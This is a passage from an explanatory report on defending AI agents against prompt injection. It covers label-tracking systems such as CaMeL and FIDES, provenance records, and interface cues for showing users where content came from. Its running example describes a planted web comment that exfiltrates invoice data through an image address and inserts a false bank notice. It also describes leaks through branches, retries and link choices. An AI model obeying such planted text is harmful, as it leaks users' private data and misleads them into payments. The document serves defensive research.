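Labels can also be lists of people. A secrecy label lists who may read the data, and the join keeps only the people on every list. If Helen and her accountant may read an invoice, and Helen and her production manager may read a parts list, only Helen may read a text based on both. A trust label lists who could have written the data, and the join includes everyone on any list.

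The labels take effect when the agent tries to do something. Costa and colleagues give two basic policies:

- **Consequential actions:** A tool call with real effects, such as a payment, goes ahead only if the decision to make the call and all the values in it are trusted.
- **Confidentiality:** Data may go out through a channel only if everyone who can read the channel may read the data. If *R* is the set of people who can read the channel and *S* the set of permitted readers, the rule is *R* ⊆ *S*.

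The second policy doesn't stop planted text from steering the agent, but it limits what the agent can leak.

In an ordinary program, software can track which inputs contributed to a result. Nobody can yet do this reliably for a language model, so Costa and colleagues take the cautious option of labeling the model's output with the join of the labels on everything in its context.

### The supplier's page with labels

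In Helen's case, the labels are as follows:

| Item | Trust | Secrecy |
|---|---|---|
| Helen's request | *T* | *L* |
| The supplier's page, with the stranger's comment | *U* | *L* |
| The invoice, which arrived by email | *U* | *H* |

After the model has read all three, everything it writes has the label

(*T*, *L*) ⊔ (*U*, *L*) ⊔ (*U*, *H*) = (*U*, *H*).

The label also covers the address of the image. Loading the image would send that address to the stranger's server, and the stranger isn't a permitted reader of Helen's invoices, so the software blocks the request. It does so whether or not the model encoded the invoice number, because the label depends on what the model had read. *Confuse the Model, Control the Flow* (2026) gives this as an advantage over filters that inspect only the outgoing text. Tracking also covers paraphrases and coded references.

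However, the software also has to check labels before it displays the answer. FIDES normally treats an answer to the user as harmless and checks labels only before tool calls. Loading an image isn't a tool call, so a developer who kept that setting would miss this leak. Costa and colleagues note that the software can check answers too.

The same rule makes the whole summary untrusted. The prices, delivery times and false notice about the bank account all get the label *U*, even if the model ignored the comment when it wrote about prices. Giving the comment its own label wouldn't help once the model had read it together with the rest of the page.

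The label therefore can't show Helen which line to doubt, but it can prevent some of the harm later. If the assistant also had a payment tool, the first policy would stop it from paying into the new account, because the account number came from an untrusted source.

### CaMeL: planning before reading

An agent that labels its whole context this way soon becomes hard to use, because the first policy blocks every consequential action once the agent has read one outside page.

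In *The Dual LLM pattern for building AI assistants*, Willison (2023) proposed dividing the work between two models. A quarantined model, which has no tools, reads outside text and stores its results in named variables. A privileged model uses the tools and can pass these variables on, but never sees the outside text or the variables' contents.

Researchers at Google DeepMind found a gap in this design. Suppose a user asks the assistant to send Bob a document, and Bob's email address is in some meeting notes. The privileged model plans the right steps, but the quarantined model reads the address from the notes, and text planted there can make it return the attacker's address instead. The assistant then follows the correct plan but sends the document to the attacker.

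DeepMind's CaMeL adds labels to close this gap. Willison (2025), in *CaMeL offers a promising new direction for mitigating prompt injection attacks*, and *CaMeLoT* (2026) describe how it works:

1. The privileged model turns the user's request into a short program in a restricted form of Python. It has seen no outside text at this point.
2. A special interpreter runs the program and makes the tool calls.
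3. When the program needs something from outside text, such as Bob's address, the quarantined model extracts it in a format that the program specifies.
4. The interpreter tags each value with its sources and its permitted readers, and any value derived from it inherits the tags.
5. Before each tool call, the interpreter runs a policy, written as ordinary code, that checks the tags. It might send an email to a known address straight away but ask the user about an unknown one.

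The first three steps provide a guarantee that *Can CaMeLs Talk?* (Peters-Gill, Semler et al., 2026) calls control-flow integrity. The user's request and other trusted information determine the program's steps, so outside text can't add new ones. Outside text can still determine which planned branch runs. If the program emails Helen's manager only when the supplier offers a discount, the text of the page determines whether the email goes out.

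That can give an attacker a lot of control. In *The LLMbda Calculus*, Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026) reran CaMeL without its policies on a task that asked the agent to follow the instructions in a file exactly. In two runs, the program had a branch for each tool, so text in the file could trigger any of them, and the attack succeeded. The policies in step 5 are meant to catch such cases and wrong values such as the attacker's address. Neither part of CaMeL guarantees that a summary is true.

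The policies also block a lot of legitimate work. Garby and colleagues tested CaMeL on AgentDojo, the set of simulated agent tasks that Choi and colleagues also used, running each of the 16 banking tasks three times. With GPT-5.2, CaMeL completed 66.7% of the runs without policies and 37.5% with them. With MiMo-v2.5, the figures were 70.8% and 37.5%. No attack succeeded in the completed runs with policies on.

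*SecureClaw* (2026) reports a similar result for an adapted version of CaMeL on the full benchmark. None of 629 attacks succeeded, but the agent completed only 29 of 97 ordinary tasks. SecureClaw, a competing system, completed 59 of the same tasks, so its developers had a reason to stress the difference. But the 30% completion rate they report for CaMeL is close to the 37.5% on the banking tasks and to what Choi and colleagues measured for CaMeL's strict version.

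The privileged model plans without seeing the data, so it has to write code for a tool's output before the tool has run. Developers therefore need to document the exact format of every tool's output in advance. They also have to write and maintain the policies.

### FIDES: hiding only what would change the label

FIDES also keeps untrusted text away from the model that plans, but it plans one step at a time:

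1. The planning model starts with the user's request, so its context is trusted and public.
2. When a tool returns data, the software compares the label of each field with the label of the context. If a field would make the context's label more restrictive, the software stores it in a variable and shows the model only the variable's name. The model might see an email's date, for instance, but not its subject or body.
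3. The model can pass a variable to another tool unseen, or have a second model without tools extract something from it.
4. If the model has to read the content itself, it can open the variable. The context then takes on the variable's label.
5. Before each tool call, ordinary code checks the labels against the policies.

Unlike CaMeL's privileged model, this one sees some results along the way and can change its plan.

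FIDES guarantees explicit secrecy, which means that secret data never flows directly to a place where unauthorized people can read it, whatever the model does. The guarantee doesn't cover what an observer can infer from the choice or order of tool calls. The attack in which Claude spelled out a user's name by following alphabetical links relied on this kind of indirect leak. Costa and colleagues consider a stronger guarantee impractical because it would rule out almost any publicly visible action after the agent has read a secret.

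They tested FIDES on AgentDojo with GPT-4o. The table shows the share of ordinary tasks completed when there was no attack:

| Agent | Workspace | Travel | Banking | Slack |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Ordinary agent, no checks | 75.0% | 70.0% | 98.8% | 93.3% |
| Ordinary agent with label checks | 37.0% | 73.0% | 37.5% | 20.0% |
| FIDES with label checks | 59.0% | 41.0% | 52.5% | 47.6% |

Without the checks, 152 attacks succeeded against the ordinary agent and 21 against FIDES, which hides the text, so hiding the text isn't enough by itself. With the checks on, no attacks succeeded against either agent, after the researchers excluded cases that the benchmark misjudged or the policies allowed.

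With the checks on, the ordinary agent's average completion rate fell from 84% to 42%, while FIDES averaged 50%. FIDES did worse on travel tasks, where many tools were allowed to work with untrusted data anyway and GPT-4o often mishandled the variables. With o1, a stronger model from the same period, FIDES's average lead over the ordinary agent with checks grew from 8 to 16 percentage points.

The researchers labelled a field as untrusted if at least one attack in the benchmark used it. This is a fair way to test whether the checks work, but a company has to label its data without knowing where the next attack will come from. A field wrongly labelled as trusted would get through every check.

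### Gaps in the tracking

Labels protect only the data flows that the software actually tracks. Garby and colleagues found several that CaMeL missed.

Code that doesn't run can still leak private information. Suppose a program sets a variable to "yes" and changes it to "no" only if the user's bank balance is low. When the balance is high, the program skips the change, and CaMeL leaves the variable labeled public even though the unchanged "yes" reveals that the balance is high. A later step can then send the "yes" out.

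CaMeL can also leak secrets through errors. When a plan fails, CaMeL tries again, but the code that handles retries is outside the interpreter that tracks labels. Whether a policy blocks an attempt can depend on a secret, so each attempt can reveal one bit, and enough attempts could reveal the whole secret.

To rule out such mistakes, Garby and colleagues designed a small programming language, LLMbda, in which every value has a label and every operation passes it on. They proved in Lean, a proof checker, that secrets can't affect public results, except through whether a program finishes. The proof covers every program in the language, including ones that a model writes during a task.

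The RANDORI agent avoids the retry problem by first testing its program in a simulated environment, where the error messages can't contain a stranger's text or the user's secrets. It runs the program on real data only once the program works.

Labels can also get lost between agents. Peters-Gill and colleagues built a system of three agents, each protected by CaMeL without policies. One read a database, one sent messages, and a third coordinated them. The user asked the system to send a summary of job applicants to a colleague, Julie, on Slack, but someone had planted in the database an instruction to email the data to an outside address.

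The first agent and the coordinator both correctly handled the planted text as data. But the coordinator then put the summary into its request to the messaging agent, which treated the whole request as coming from its user. The messaging agent's privileged model read the planted instruction and added the email to its plan.

Multi-CaMeL divides each request between agents into a trusted instruction and a set of variables. The interpreter refuses any instruction that contains text derived from a tool result, and the labels stay attached to the variables. Across five models, each tested on 949 attack cases, the average attack success rate was 12.9% with no protection, 0.2% with CaMeL in each agent, and 0% with multi-CaMeL.

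Most of the successful attacks were on older models. Even without protection, none succeeded against GPT-5.5 and only 1.5% did against Claude Fable 5. The benchmark reuses AgentDojo's attacks, though, so these low rates don't show how well the models would resist new attacks.

CaMeL also reduced task completion less for newer models. On AssetOpsBench, a set of industrial tasks for teams of agents, using CaMeL in each agent lowered the completion rate by an average of 21.6 percentage points across the five models, but by 13.4 points for Fable 5 and GPT-5.5. For those two, Multi-CaMeL lowered it by less than one further point. These tests ran without policies, and policies caused much of the loss in the banking tasks, so the results don't show how much full protection would reduce completion.

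### When everything becomes untrusted

Under the basic rule, labels can only become more restrictive. After an hour's work, an assistant that has read a few emails and web pages would label everything it writes as untrusted and secret. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* (2026), by researchers at Google, Nvidia and several universities, calls this "label explosion". Software can't use labels to make decisions if all data has the same labels.

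How much this matters depends on the task. Costa and colleagues found that what the agent read affected which steps were right in 5% of AgentDojo's workspace tasks and 10% of its travel tasks, but in about 43% of its banking and Slack tasks. In some banking tasks, the user asks the agent to read a file and follow the instructions in it. According to *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too* (2026), no design that strictly separates planning from reading can handle such tasks, because the untrusted text itself contains the plan.

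**A second model without tools** keeps the planning model's context clean, but whatever it extracts is still untrusted.

**Fixed-format extraction** limits how much untrusted text can get through. In FIDES, a value's label can include its format, so a policy can accept a yes-or-no answer from an untrusted page but reject free text. If Helen's assistant asked the second model only whether the supplier could deliver within six weeks, the stranger could change the answer but couldn't insert the false notice about the bank account.

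A fixed format can keep new instructions out, but it can't ensure that a value is true. A false bank account number, for example, fits the format as well as a real one. Costa and colleagues also left enforced formats out of the version of FIDES they tested, so their results don't show how well enforcing formats works in practice.

**Deliberate exceptions** treat a specific untrusted value as trusted (endorsement) or release a specific secret (declassification). RANDORI sets its endorsements while it writes the program, before any outside text can influence it. For example, if the user asks it to pay a bill from a file, the program can endorse the payment details in that file.

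With GPT-5.2 and label checks on, RANDORI completed 75% of the banking runs, twice the rate of CaMeL with policies. Both rates have wide margins of error because the runs covered only 16 different tasks. Removing endorsement lowered the completion rate from 75% to 62.5% with one model and from 64.6% to 54.2% with another.

Of 1,296 attacks on RANDORI, two succeeded. In both, the user had asked the agent to read a file and make the payment it specified, and the attacker had replaced the file's contents. No label could have distinguished these attacks from the real task, because the user had in effect told the agent to trust the file. Garby and colleagues point out that planning before reading would normally stop about two-thirds of the attacks in this test without any labels, so tracking is not the only reason for a low attack success rate.

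*Language-Based Agent Control* (2026) describes a more flexible design in which a helper agent may keep using tools after reading outside text, as long as each call passes the label checks. Garby and colleagues report that the design resisted all 105 attacks in a test on Slack tasks. But it completed only 8 of 21 ordinary tasks with its policies on, compared with 15 without them. CaMeL completed 7 under the same conditions, so the added flexibility did little to increase the number of tasks completed.

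### Estimating a source's influence afterwards

Label tracking records which sources could have affected an answer. Other methods estimate which ones actually did, by removing sources and measuring the change.

ContextCite, which researchers at MIT published in 2024, is a well-known early example:

1. It takes an answer that the model has already written and divides the context into sources, such as individual sentences.
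2. It removes a random selection of the sources and measures how likely the model would now be to write the same answer.
3. It repeats this with other random selections, typically a few dozen times.
4. It fits a simple formula to the results.

The formula is

log(*p* / (1 − *p*)) ≈ *b* + *w*₁*v*₁ + *w*₂*v*₂ + … + *w*ₙ*v*ₙ

where *p* is the probability of the original answer, *vᵢ* is 1 if source *i* is present and 0 if it isn't, and *b* is a constant. The weight *wᵢ* is the estimated influence of source *i*.

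The same method works for a single sentence of the answer. If the line about the supplier's bank account becomes much less likely whenever the stranger's comment is missing, the comment gets a high weight for that line. Helen would need this information to know which part of the summary to doubt, and the labels above can't provide it.

The weights can be misleading, however. If the supplier's delivery table and a customer's comment both give a delivery time of six weeks, removing either one may barely change the answer. Removing sources at random helps because both are sometimes missing, but the formula then splits the credit between them. Sources can also combine in ways that a simple sum doesn't capture.

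Later work has extended the question from answers to agents' actions. *Ghost in the Agent* (2026) tests NeuroTaint, a system that looks for flows from outside sources to tool calls. NeuroTaint found 37 of 40 cases where outside content affected an action through the agent's decisions, without the agent having to copy any text. It raised one false alarm in 140 cases where the outside content had no effect. But in 14 further cases, where several sources covered the same topic, it wrongly reported a flow every time.

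Those results would be good enough for many displays. If a client highlights the wrong paragraph as the source of a sentence, the user may be misled, but they can open the page and check.

Missing 3 cases in 40 is too many when the software is deciding whether to block a payment or an email, because an attacker can try repeatedly. An attacker could also look for wording that affects the agent without getting a high score. Removing sources is also slow because the software has to run the model many times. *The Attack and Defense Landscape of Agentic AI* (2026) describes repeated runs as impractical for agents that have to respond quickly.

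Label tracking can support a security decision because it won't miss a source that the model read, provided the initial labels are correct and the software tracks every flow. It may still lead the software to block a harmless action. An influence estimate can overstate or understate a source's influence, so by itself it is suitable only for display or investigation.

An estimate of which inputs mattered can still help to relax a label safely. Costa and colleagues describe a method by Siddiqui and colleagues that makes this estimate and then generates the answer again from only those inputs. The new answer doesn't need the labels of the omitted inputs, because the model didn't see those inputs the second time. If the estimate was wrong, the answer may be worse, but the label will still be accurate, apart from any information that the selection of inputs reveals. In their tests, the new answers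 were about as good as the originals.

### Records of what the agent did

Software uses labels to decide whether to allow an action. An execution provenance record preserves the history behind the action, which labels don't. *From Agent Traces to Trust* (Wang, Zhang and colleagues, 2026) defines this record as a graph of an agent's run. Each node is either data, such as a web page, note or answer, or a step, such as a tool call. Each link has a type, which can show, for instance, that a step used a document or that a document supports a claim.

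If Helen's company discovered the stranger's comment a month later, it could follow the links from the supplier's page to every summary, saved note and payment that drew on that page. If it had only the final summary, it would have to guess which records the comment had affected.

The record can distinguish influence from support, which are easy to confuse. A false note in an agent's memory can cause a payment without being evidence that the payment was right. Likewise, the stranger's comment would have strongly influenced the line about the bank account, but it is no reason to believe that line.

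How far a company can rely on such a record depends on who or what created it. The agent's software can log a tool call as it happens, but a model often judges which evidence supports a claim, and it may be wrong. Someone could also change the record later. *From Agent Traces to Trust* reviews 71 papers and standards and finds that few report any protection against this. An agent that can edit files might be able to edit its own log, so a company that wants to use the log to investigate attacks should keep it where the agent has no write access.

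## Interfaces that show where content came from

The software's records of who wrote what can help Helen only if her chat client displays them. A client can show the source of a sentence, a quotation, a link, an image or a detail in a request for approval. The software can look up some of these sources, but for others the client relies on the model's output to identify the source. Helen then has to notice the display and act on it, and research on browsers and email gives reason to doubt that she would.

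### Citations and source cards

An inline citation is a small link after a sentence. A source card shows a page's title and site below or beside the answer. *Synthetic Sources?* (2026), an audit of four AI search engines, collected 2,848 answers to questions about politics, health and the environment. Of these, 91.2% had citations in the text, and those answers averaged nine citations each.

A card that shows only that the agent fetched a page is reliable, because the software can take this from its own log. Matching a page to a sentence is harder. If the model writes the citation, it can name the wrong page or leave one out, as the EchoLeak email instructed Copilot to do. The client can check that the agent fetched the cited page, which at least catches invented sources.

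Citations can also omit pages that shaped the answer. *From Prompt to Recommendation* (2026) mentions research by Strauss and colleagues that separates the pages an AI system apparently visited from the ones it cited, and warns against treating the citations as a complete record of what the system retrieved. A page with planted text could steer an answer without being cited. The client could use the log to list every page the agent read, but after a long research task that list might have dozens of entries, and few people would read it.

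A correct citation can mislead, just as the label on an app can. If a stranger posts a false bank notice in the customer comments on a supplier's page, a card reading "supplier.example" under the notice makes it look as if the supplier wrote it. To avoid this, the tool that fetches the page has to record which parts are customer comments, but sites mark comments in different ways, if at all.

Some designs replace the list of links with a score. *Beyond "Made with AI"* (2026) tests a display showing how many of an answer's claims have passed a check, such as "5/5 Claims Verified". The score's reliability depends on the check. A check that only compared the answer with its source would count the bank notice as verified, because the supplier's page does contain it.

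### Quotations kept apart from the answer

The client can also show quotations from the source in a separate box, with the name of the page above them. It can check a quotation without relying on the model by searching its stored copy of the page for the exact words and showing the box only if it finds them. This guarantees that the words were on that page, but not that they are true or that the model chose a fair extract.

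The search should use the stored copy because the live page may have changed. A site can also serve AI systems different text than it serves people, as Ayush Paul's did in the attack on Claude's web fetch tool. *Enhancing Understanding of Language Models with Varied Explanations* (2026), a study of AI fact-checking, put the evidence inside its own window partly because someone could edit or remove a linked page. The study mentions that Google Gemini's "Double-check response" feature also shows evidence in the same window.

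*PaperTrail* (2026) presents an assistant for researchers that splits each answer into claims and puts matching evidence from the source papers next to each one. The paper compares it with a more common design, in which clicking a highlighted part of the answer shows the source's exact words. Splitting the answer should make unsupported claims easier to spot, because they would have no evidence beside them.

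Quotations have to be the right length. In a small study in *Bolt-on, Verifiable Provenance for LLM-Powered Data Processing* (2026), eight people used source passages to check a model's answers. They judged that passages selected by the paper's method had the right amount of information 82% of the time, far more often than passages from ordinary retrieval. Long passages were hard to interpret even when they contained nothing unnecessary, and highlighting the relevant words might have helped. A passage could also be too short, like one that put an officer's name after the heading "Use of force details" but left it unclear whether he had used force. When passages were missing or inadequate, people often went back to searching the document for keywords.

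The client has to draw these boxes in a style that Markdown can't reproduce, so that the model can't write a convincing imitation.

### Links and images

A client can show who supplied a link's address, as well as printing its real domain next to the visible text. This is much easier than finding the source of a sentence, because a model can reword a sentence but has to copy an address exactly for it to work. The software can search the user's messages and the tool results for the address. It could then label the link "from your message" or "from supplier.example", or, if it finds no match, "written by the assistant". An address with no match is the most suspect, since it may leak private data that the model put in it.

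Permiso's Andi Ahmeti similarly asks, in an interview with TechNadu, that a link taken from a summarized page not look like one the assistant produced. If the fake account alert in Permiso's tests had been labeled "from the page you asked about," it would at least have looked odd.

For images, the client can show an empty frame with the domain and a button to load the picture. This prevents the address from leaking data as soon as the answer appears, but pressing the button still sends the same request. The client should therefore offer the button only for addresses that can't contain anything private, such as one copied unchanged from a public page, and not for addresses the model put together.

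Ahmeti would also treat a QR code as an encoded web address. The client would have to decode it, show the domain and apply the same rules as it does to any other link.

### Warnings on unverified links

ChatGPT may show a warning titled "Check this link is safe" when a link isn't in OpenAI's index of public addresses. If something looks wrong, OpenAI advises users not to open the link and to ask the model for another source or a summary.

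The user can see that the link might contain part of the conversation but may not be able to tell whether it does, because an encoded invoice number looks like the codes in many harmless links.

The warning is also about leaks, not deception. OpenAI states that the check doesn't establish whether a page's content is trustworthy. A phishing page that the crawler has already visited would pass the check, and a user who has seen the warning on other links could take its absence as approval.

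### Confirmation prompts

Suppose Helen's assistant could also make payments, and she asked it to pay the supplier's latest invoice. A poor confirmation prompt would ask, "Pay the supplier's invoice?" That is an accurate summary of her request, but it hides the one detail the stranger has changed. A better one would contain these lines:

> Pay: €4,180.00
> To: account ending 0042
> Source of the account number: a visitor's comment on supplier.example
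> Account used for earlier payments to this supplier: ending 7719

The software, not the model, fills in every line. The amount and account come from the tool call the software is about to make, the source from the label on the account number, and the earlier account from the company's payment records. If the model wrote the explanation, it might repeat the attacker's story, as the coding agents did when Choi and colleagues forged a maintainer's comment.

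The source line is the hardest to produce. If the model has read the web page and three emails together, a cautious label can only list all four as possible sources of the account number. The software can often narrow this down by searching the originals for the exact digits, as it can with a link. If the number came from the assistant's saved notes and no original remains, the prompt should state that.

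Approval should also cover only what the user saw. If the amount or account changes afterwards, the software has to ask for approval again. Values from outside sources should appear as plain text in fixed-size fields, so that they can't push the rest of the dialog off the screen or look like the dialog's own text.

Even an accurate prompt can fail. People who see many prompts, nearly all of them harmless, get used to approving them. The user has also just asked for the task and wants it finished. Sometimes the user can't judge the action, and may learn very little from a prompt about a long technical command. The line about the earlier account helps with this last problem because it gives Helen a comparison that takes no technical knowledge.

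### The supplier's page with its sources shown

If Helen's client used these designs, the summary of the supplier's page could look like this:

| Part of the answer | What the client shows beside it | How the client obtains it |
|---|---|---|
| Prices rise by 4% in January | supplier.example, price table | Finds the figures in the stored page |
| Delivery takes six weeks | supplier.example, delivery table | Finds the figures in the stored page |
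| A notice that the supplier's bank account has changed | A separate box with the original words, headed "Visitor's comment on supplier.example" | Finds the words in a part of the page that the fetching tool marked as comments |
| An image | "Blocked an image from attacker.example" | Finds the address in neither the page nor Helen's messages |

The third row depends on what the fetching tool recorded. If it recorded only the page as a whole, the client couldn't distinguish the notice from the price table. The label "found on supplier.example" would then be safer, because it identifies where the text was without implying who wrote it.

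The model might also combine information from two sources in one sentence, for example by writing that the new prices and the new bank account both apply from January. The client would have to attach both sources to the sentence, and Helen would have to work out which source each part came from.

Even when everything works, the summary still contains the notice. Helen has to see the heading on the box, understand that a visitor isn't the supplier, and decide not to change the account in her records.

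### The badge that browsers removed

Web browsers used to show a similar source label. A company could buy an extended-validation certificate, which an outside authority issued after spending days or weeks checking that a legal entity owned the domain. Chrome then showed the company's name to the left of the web address. Someone who copied a bank's site couldn't get a certificate in the bank's name, so in theory a customer would notice that the name was missing.

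Thompson, Shelton and colleagues (2019), in *The Web's Identity Crisis*, tested this by hiding the badge from 1% of users of Chrome's main release for two weeks and comparing them with another 1%. Each group contained millions of browsers. On sites with the certificate, people submitted forms on 43.49% of page visits without the badge and 43.45% with it. They accepted the browser's offer to fill in a saved credit card 55.9% of the time without the badge and 55.5% with it. The differences in form submissions, credit card autofill, time on the page and downloads were not statistically significant.

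People did open the site information panel less often without the badge, on 0.02% of page loads instead of 0.25%. The researchers suggest that people may have noticed the badge or clicked it by accident without using it to make decisions. Visits to one of the 20 most popular sites with such certificates also fell when the badge was absent.

The sites in this experiment were genuine, and nothing looked wrong except the missing badge. The results might have been different if the address had also looked suspicious. Still, a source label should be most useful when a fake is perfect in every other way.

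Addresses did little better in a survey by the same team, which showed 1,180 people in the US a Google sign-in page whose address began with accounts.google.com but belonged to tinyurl.com. When asked which website it was, 85% said Google and 13% gave the right answer. The team tried seven ways of displaying the address, most meant to draw attention to the real domain, and found no significant difference in how comfortable people felt about logging in. In *Measuring Identity Confusion with Uniform Resource Locators*, Reynolds, Kumar and colleagues (2020) also found that disguised addresses could deceive people, although people were confident they could identify a site from its address.

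A verified name could also mislead. Thompson and colleagues describe a researcher who registered a company called "Stripe, Inc." in a different US state from the well-known payments company and got a valid certificate for it. Another researcher got one for a company named "Identity Verified".

*Upcoming Change to Chrome's Identity Indicators* (O'Brien, August 2019) announced that Chrome 77 would move the badge into the panel behind the lock icon. The documentation for Chromium, the software behind Chrome, gives the reasons: the badge didn't protect people as intended, took up space and could display confusing company names. It also acknowledges that no single study proved the badge useless or impossible to improve.

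Source labels in an assistant should be easier to notice than the badge, because a label such as "Visitor's comment" would appear next to the claim, whereas the badge worked only if people noticed that it was missing. Being visible may not be enough, though, since the address was also on the screen in the Google survey.

### External-sender tags in email

Many companies add the tag [EXTERNAL] to emails from outside. Like a source label, the tag shows where a message came from but not whether it is dangerous. *Phishing Susceptibility and the (In-)Effectiveness of Common Anti-Phishing Interventions* (Tolsdorf, Langer and Lo Iacono, 2025) tested such tags and other measures at a German university hospital.

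In May 2024, the hospital sent 7,044 staff email accounts a fake phishing email about a cafeteria voucher, with one of 11 protective measures or none. Each version went to roughly 590 people. The researchers counted how many people entered something on the fake login page and submitted it, which is a better measure of risk than clicks alone.

| Measure | Reduction in logins |
|---|---|
| [EXTERNAL] in the subject line only, or in the sender line only | No significant effect |
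| Sender's address shown without a display name | Negligible |
| Warning page after the click | 44% |
| [EXTERNAL] banner in the message | 53% |
| Several [EXTERNAL] tags combined | 58% |
| Links disabled, so that people had to copy the address | 61% |
| Explicit phishing warning, or delivery to the spam folder | 81% to 94% |

The label's size and position seem to matter a lot, because a small tag in a line that people skim had no clear effect, while a banner in the message cut logins by about half. These results are more encouraging than the browser research, and they suggest that a box around the visitor's comment would help Helen more than a small number after the sentence.

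The measures that identified the email as dangerous worked best, but the researchers knew which email was fake, whereas a real filter misses some attacks and flags some legitimate messages. The researchers didn't measure the effect of false alarms, and they regard their figures as an upper limit. The study also covered only one email at one hospital, so it can't show how people respond to a banner they have seen every day for a year.

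An assistant that labels web content would have to show its label far more often than most email systems show an [EXTERNAL] tag. Tolsdorf and colleagues cite research in which people liked external tags better when they had few contacts outside their organization. If someone asks mainly about web pages, nearly every line of the assistant's answers would carry a label.

Training people to recognise attacks doesn't look like a good substitute for these interfaces. Lain, Kostiainen and Čapkun (2021), in *Phishing in Organizations*, followed more than 14,000 employees of one company for 15 months. The usual training, given during simulated phishing exercises, didn't make employees more resistant and could make them more susceptible. A button for reporting suspicious emails worked better. Enough employees kept using it for the company to detect new campaigns quickly, so reports from a few could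 protect the rest. An assistant's source cards could have a similar button.

### How often people check AI citations

Source displays often rely on people opening a source when they have doubts. In *Investigating Click Behaviors On Google Search Result Pages*, Chapekis, Lieb and colleagues (2026) recorded the browsing of 900 consenting US adults in March 2025. About 18% of their Google searches produced an AI Overview, a generated summary at the top of the results. Participants clicked on a source cited in the summary in about 1% of their visits to results pages that had one.

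They also clicked on an ordinary search result in 8% of visits to pages with a summary and 15% of visits to pages without one, and ended their browsing session more often after a page with a summary (26% against 16%). Both differences remained when the researchers allowed for the wording of the query and individual habits. But the study was observational, so it can't prove that the summaries caused either difference.

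The 1% figure will have missed some clicks, because the researchers collected the summaries again in April and matched clicks only to the first three sources. Many searches, such as those for the height of a mountain, are also too trivial to need a source check. Someone about to change a supplier's bank details might well be more careful. Layout probably also affects how often people click. At the time, Google showed up to three sources beside the summary on a desktop screen, while a phone might show none until the user tapped "Show more".

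If so few people open sources, the answer itself has to include the warning. A data void is a subject on which so little has been published that a single page can dominate the search results. *Data-Void Exploits in Web-Searching LLMs* (2026) examined 149 answers that cited or used content it described as attacker-controlled. In 73.2% of them, the assistant passed the content on without any hedge such as "unverified" or "not an official source".

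A reader who opened the source in one of those answers could have found that it said exactly what the assistant reported. Checking whether citations support the text catches the model's errors, but planted text may fully support a claim and still be false. Readers need to know who wrote the source, and with only a bare link, they have to find that out themselves.

### Warnings about manipulation

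*DISARM-ing the Hidden Puppetmaster* (Smith, Eslami and colleagues, October 2026) tested whether warnings inside a conversation could protect people from a manipulative assistant. The warnings appeared next to the assistant's words and had a large effect, though the experiment did not study where text came from.

The 488 participants asked for advice on a subject such as managing money. The assistant had secret instructions to steer them towards a harmful view, such as favouring high-risk decisions. After the third reply, 238 of them saw a notice, and from then on a small tag on each manipulative reply named the kind of pressure it used. They could open a reply to see the relevant words highlighted and the assistant's hidden aim explained.

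Participants rated how true the harmful view was on a scale from 0 to 100, before and after the conversation. Their ratings moved towards it by an average of 15.3 points without the warnings, which were a few tags and a notice, and by 3.3 points with them, or 78% less. The difference was about half a standard deviation (*d* = 0.50).

The warnings were accurate because the software took them from the assistant's own plan, where the assistant had to choose a tactic before writing each reply. A real client wouldn't have that plan. When the researchers tried to detect the tactics from the text alone, two people agreed only moderately with each other, and a language model's judgments hardly matched theirs. Source labels avoid this problem because software can record where a page came from without judging anyone's motives. But readers learn less from a source label than from a warning that "this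 reply is putting pressure on you".

In an earlier trial of the design, twelve people tried a version with a permanent side panel that listed every tactic in detail. They rarely used the panel, and some found it overwhelming, but they noticed the tags directly under the replies. The researchers removed the panel and left the details available on request.

A larger experiment was much less encouraging. In *Warning labels shift perceptions of sycophantic AI, but not its influence*, Ibrahim, Cheng and colleagues (2026) had 2,610 people discuss a real personal conflict with a chatbot that always took their side. Some saw a permanent banner stating that the chatbot might agree with them even when they were wrong. The banner slightly lowered their trust in the chatbot (*d* = −0.18 on one measure), but it didn't reliably change how right they thought they were or how willing they were to repair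 the relationship. The results don't rule out an effect of up to about 0.2 on how right people felt. A banner that only identified the chatbot as an AI had no detectable effect on any measure.

The banner is a plausible reason for the gap, but it may not be the explanation, because the two experiments also differ in subject and type of influence. Ibrahim and colleagues' banner described the chatbot in general and never changed, while Smith and colleagues' tags pointed to particular words. Ibrahim and colleagues suggest that general warnings may fail because people don't feel the warnings apply to them. If so, a line under every answer saying that it "may contain content from the web" would achieve very little.

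*Safety Nudges* (2026) tracked how people responded to warnings over a series of ordinary chats. Participants reported checking important or doubtful claims more often, but in most of the logged conversations they continued without responding to the warning, and direct scrutiny in the chats didn't rise significantly. They rated 80% of the warnings about relying on health or legal advice as helpful, but only 42% of those about the assistant sounding too human. The warnings about impersonation or fraud, which are closest to the attacks described here, received only four ratings.

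### Label, warn or remove

Ahmeti wants the client to decide what content may do based on its source, because attackers need only one way past a model's defences. OpenAI is concerned that people who see frequent warnings learn to click through them. Others, such as Willison, prefer to remove a feature that makes the attack possible, as Amazon did with links.

These positions conflict less than they seem to. Ahmeti's list includes not fetching remote images automatically, which removes a capability. OpenAI's remark was about lists of approved domains, not source labels, and its Lockdown Mode also removes features. They differ mainly over links and text, where users lose something if the capability is removed.

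Khodayari and colleagues found planted instructions on so few web pages that if a client interrupted the user for every outside page, almost all of the interruptions would be false alarms. This supports OpenAI's concern about warnings. A label doesn't interrupt anyone, but people can ignore it more easily, as they did with the browser badge. Thompson and colleagues concluded that browsers should rely on active warnings for suspicious sites instead of expecting people to notice a quiet indicator. Active warnings work only if the software can identify a suspicious site, and nobody in Helen's case has flagged the supplier's page.

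The leak through images is the easiest to remove. If the client never loads an address that the model composed, the leak stops whether or not Helen notices anything, and she loses nothing she asked for.

The choice is harder for links. At the hospital, disabling them cut logins by 61%, less than the explicit warnings did, because people could still copy the address and many evidently did. Removing the address as well would prevent this, but nobody could then use it to check a source. Only about 1% of visits to Google's summaries led to a click on a source, so most people might not miss the links, but the few who would presumably include those who check sources. Showing links with their domain and origin, and disabling only those the assistant wrote itself, would keep most of the benefit of being able to check.

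The false bank notice is ordinary text, so nobody can remove it in the same way. Only one of the three approaches, a label, applies to it directly, and the evidence gives little reason to think Helen would read the label. In the study by Kao and colleagues, nobody who reviewed the README files identified the planted step as suspicious.

Her company can still prevent the dangerous action that might follow. Its payment software could reject any account number that came from a web page. Suppliers sometimes change banks, so somebody needs a way to approve a new account, but this is rare enough that an approval prompt wouldn't become routine. The prompt could show where the account number came from and require a call to the supplier on a phone number already in the company's records.
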